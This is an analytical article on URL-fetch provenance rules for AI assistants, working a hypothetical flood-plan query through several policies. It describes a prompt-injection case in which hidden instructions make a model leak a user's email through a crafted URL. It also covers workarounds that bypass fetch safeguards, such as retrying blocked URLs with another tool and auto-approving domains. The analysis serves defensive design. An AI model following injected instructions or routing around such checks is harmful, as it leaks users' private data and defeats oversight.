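In this hypothetical example, a resident asks an assistant whether their county's new flood plan accounts for last year's rainfall, and the assistant tries to read six pages.

| Page | Source of the address | Any URL | User and search URLs only | Public index with a warning |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The county's flood page | The user's message | Read | Read | Read |
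| A newspaper report | A search result | Read | Read | Read |
| Page 2 of the county's list of past floods | A link on the flood page | Read | Refused, then read when the user pastes the link | Read |
| The rainfall service's manual | Guessed from an older manual's address | Read | Refused, then read after a search | Read |
| Last year's rainfall at the local station | Composed by following the manual | Read | Refused and never read | Read after a warning |
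| The flood plan, published an hour ago | A link on the flood page | Read | Refused, then read when the user pastes the link | Read after a warning |

The example assumes that the crawler has recorded the four pages the assistant reads without a warning, that the user approves both warnings, and that the assistant can then load the page. Under the middle policy, the assistant searches after each refusal and asks for the two missing county links in one message.

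| Count | Any URL | User and search URLs only | Public index with a warning |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pages read | 6 | 5 | 6 |
| Fetches refused or held for approval | 0 | 4 | 2 |
| Extra searches | 0 | 4 | 0 |
| User interruptions | 0 | 1 | 2 |

The middle policy misses only one page, but that page has the rainfall figure the question depends on. The user would have to look it up on the rainfall service's website and paste it into the chat. Under the index policy, the assistant might have looked for another website instead of showing a warning. The user would then have been interrupted less, but might have received a journalist's summary of the plan instead of the plan itself.

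A fourth policy, Anthropic's default for developers, also accepts links on fetched pages. It would allow both county links, leaving two refusals and no interruptions, though the rainfall figure would still be missing. For this user, Anthropic's July 2026 repair to the Claude app therefore results in two more refusals and one more message.

Suppose a reader's comment under the newspaper report contains hidden instructions to send the user's email address to a stranger's website, and the model follows them. With no rule, the email address leaks without the user noticing. Under the middle policy, the software refuses the request. Under the index policy, the user may see a third warning soon after approving two harmless requests. OpenAI fears that repeated warnings like these teach people to click through them.

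### Evidence of the cost

Nobody appears to have published data on how often assistants complete tasks with and without OpenAI's or Anthropic's URL rules. *Fetch, Read, Reuse* comes closest, but it reports failed fetches and outdated copies, not the share of tasks that failed because of a URL rule.

Its results also show that fetches can fail for reasons unrelated to the rules, so a failed fetch is poor evidence against them. None of the three API services tested for this, from OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI, read text that a page supplied only through JavaScript. Anthropic's fetch tool refused 19% of a set of public plain-text files and gave the site's domain as the reason. After a test page returned an error once, Anthropic's tool did not request it again for the rest of the test, up to about 11 hours, even though the researchers had repaired the page. A user could easily mistake any of these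 problems for a provenance rule at work.

Failures also cost money. Chen and colleagues found that a failed fetch of a small page used about as many input tokens as a successful one. They didn't test refusals under a provenance rule, but a refusal also gives the model an error to process and often leads to another search.

*ActGov* (2026), a research system that checks an agent's actions against a policy, has more detailed conditions for URLs than OpenAI or Anthropic. It can accept a download link, for instance, if the link comes from a page already tied to the user's task and untrusted text hasn't influenced it. Such conditions might allow some of the links that the Claude app now refuses. But they aren't OpenAI's or Anthropic's rules, so they don't show how much users and developers lose under those rules.

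In *Can not open generated hyperlinks in desktop browser*, an undated thread on OpenAI's forum, a developer complains about links to a flashcard site that reads its questions and answers from the URL. ChatGPT was meant to write a set of cards and give the user a link to them. ChatGPT's older check, url_safe, approved the site's bare address but rejected it with the cards attached, even though they held only facts such as the capital of Japan. The links worked on a phone but not on a desktop computer, which the developer took for a bug.

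The phone was probably the less protected of the two, since OpenAI's mobile apps lacked the check at first. The rejection was reasonable, because a flashcard page has to read the text in its URL, and a hostile page on the same hosting service could read a user's private data in the same way and send it elsewhere. The check could not distinguish between the two kinds of page, so a useful, harmless product stopped working.

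Another thread, *OpenAI Blocking ChatGPT from accessing public posts on the OpenAI Dev Board?*, is much weaker evidence. A user suspected that ChatGPT could open only search results, partly because of a ChatGPT answer that OpenAI was blocking it. Someone replied that this explanation was probably hallucinated, since ChatGPT often cites the forum. A model's explanation for a failed fetch is unreliable unless the software gave it the reason.

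Developers who use Anthropic's API can now collect better evidence by counting how often the error `url_not_in_prior_context` appears and how often Claude then finds the page another way. OpenAI and Anthropic could do the same across millions of conversations, and publishing the results would settle much of the argument about how much users and developers lose under these rules.

### What each workaround gives up

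The simplest workaround is for the user to paste the address. If they paste a single link to a page they chose, they give up very little protection. They give up more if they paste a long email full of someone else's links, or an address the model wrote that they haven't checked. If the task needs a data query, pasting works only if the user knows how to write the query.

Searching first is safer because the model still can't write private data into the URL of a fetch, though an attacker can try to get pages into the search results. Searching won't find a private document, a page published in the last hour, or the results of a particular data query, and it may return the manual for the wrong version of a product.

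In Anthropic's API, adding the rainfall service to allowed_domains would not make the query work, because the ban on constructed URLs still applies. But in a version of Claude Desktop that uses other companies' model services, an organisation's network allowlist controls fetching, according to Anthropic's *Web search and web fetch*. Where such a list replaces a provenance rule, users lose the protection against content leaks on every listed site.

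Developers can also write their own fetch tool, which runs outside Anthropic's check. *tool_web_fetch*, a documentation page for a Posit programming library, explains that Claude can't construct URLs and directs users of OpenAI's and other companies' models to a separate fetch program. Using a separate program is a sensible way to add a missing feature, but the developer then has to supply the restrictions too.

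The open-source project jupyterlite-ai adds AI models to a programming notebook. If web_fetch returns the error `url_not_allowed`, the project's agent must retry the same URL with a tool called browser_fetch, if available, before it turns to search. The project's documentation lists the developer's own domain restrictions among the causes of the error, so browser_fetch could request a page that the developer meant to block. The tool can read a page only if the site lets code on other websites do so. This offers little protection, since an attacker can configure a site to allow it, and a simple request usually reaches the server even when the browser withholds the reply.

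An unrestricted tool has none of the protection against content leaks. For the rainfall query, the developer could instead write a tool that accepts only a station number and a year, checks both, and builds the URL itself. With 500 stations and 50 years, the model could choose among 25,000 queries, so each call could carry about 14.6 bits. Every request would go to the rainfall service, whose logs an attacker normally can't read. Writing such a tool takes more work, and the developer has to repeat it for each service.

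### Claude Code's approval per domain

Claude Code instead asks the user for permission to use WebFetch, its fetch tool. According to Anthropic's documentation, the prompt includes an option not to ask again. If the user picks this, Claude Code saves a rule for the whole domain that applies to every later session in the same code repository. Claude Code enforces the rule in its own software, so instructions to the model can't change it.

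In the flood example, this policy would require three approvals, one each for the county, the newspaper and the rainfall service. The assistant could then read all six pages, including the rainfall query, and a second task on the same sites would require no more approvals.

A user who approves a domain lets Claude send data to it as well as read its pages. If the user permanently allows a stranger's blog to read one article, and the article contains hidden instructions, Claude can send private data to the blog in another URL without asking for permission again. A provenance rule would block that URL. Domains that Anthropic approves in advance carry the same risk. Vulners' security advisory *Claude Code* reports that Anthropic had pre-approved all of huggingface.co, including pages that attackers controlled.

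The prompts also annoy people. yurukusa's *Fix Claude Code WebFetch Domain Matching* cites an issue report, with 46 reactions, that prompts still appeared under a setting meant to allow every domain. The page offers a script that automatically approves chosen domains. Forty-six reactions are weak evidence of how common the annoyance is, but a user who tries to allow every domain has chosen to give up this protection entirely. Users can also switch to Claude Code's auto mode, in which a classifier reviews actions instead of the user.

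As with web_fetch, these permissions don't cover Claude's command line. Anthropic suggests denying programs such as curl, which can reach any URL. Because a command can be written in many ways, it also suggests limiting the network access of the sandbox where commands run.

### A refused fetch against a silent leak

The case against the rules is that they burden everyone to stop a rare event. Most constructed URLs are harmless, and public data services are designed to receive them. Anthropic's rule also applies when there is no private data to steal. A program that handles only public weather data still can't use web_fetch on a URL it constructs, because the url_sources setting can only remove link sources. Its developer has good reason to write an unrestricted tool, and may later connect that tool to private data without reconsidering the risk. Anthropic's rule would then offer no protection,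 which seems to be the best argument for loosening it.

Still, a user can recover from a refusal by pasting a link or looking up a number, but nobody can recall a leaked email or medical detail from a stranger's server log, and the user may never find out it is there.

Suppose that each refusal wastes one minute of a user's time and that a leak does as much harm as 100 lost hours. The rule would then be worth having if it prevented at least one leak for every 6,000 refusals. Both figures are invented, and nobody has published the real ratio. For an assistant that can read someone's inbox, 100 hours may well be too low, and refusing is the better default. For the weather program, a leak does no harm, so no refusal is justified. Anthropic could let developers of such programs turn off the ban on constructed URLs, provided that the API turned it back on as soon as they connected a private source.
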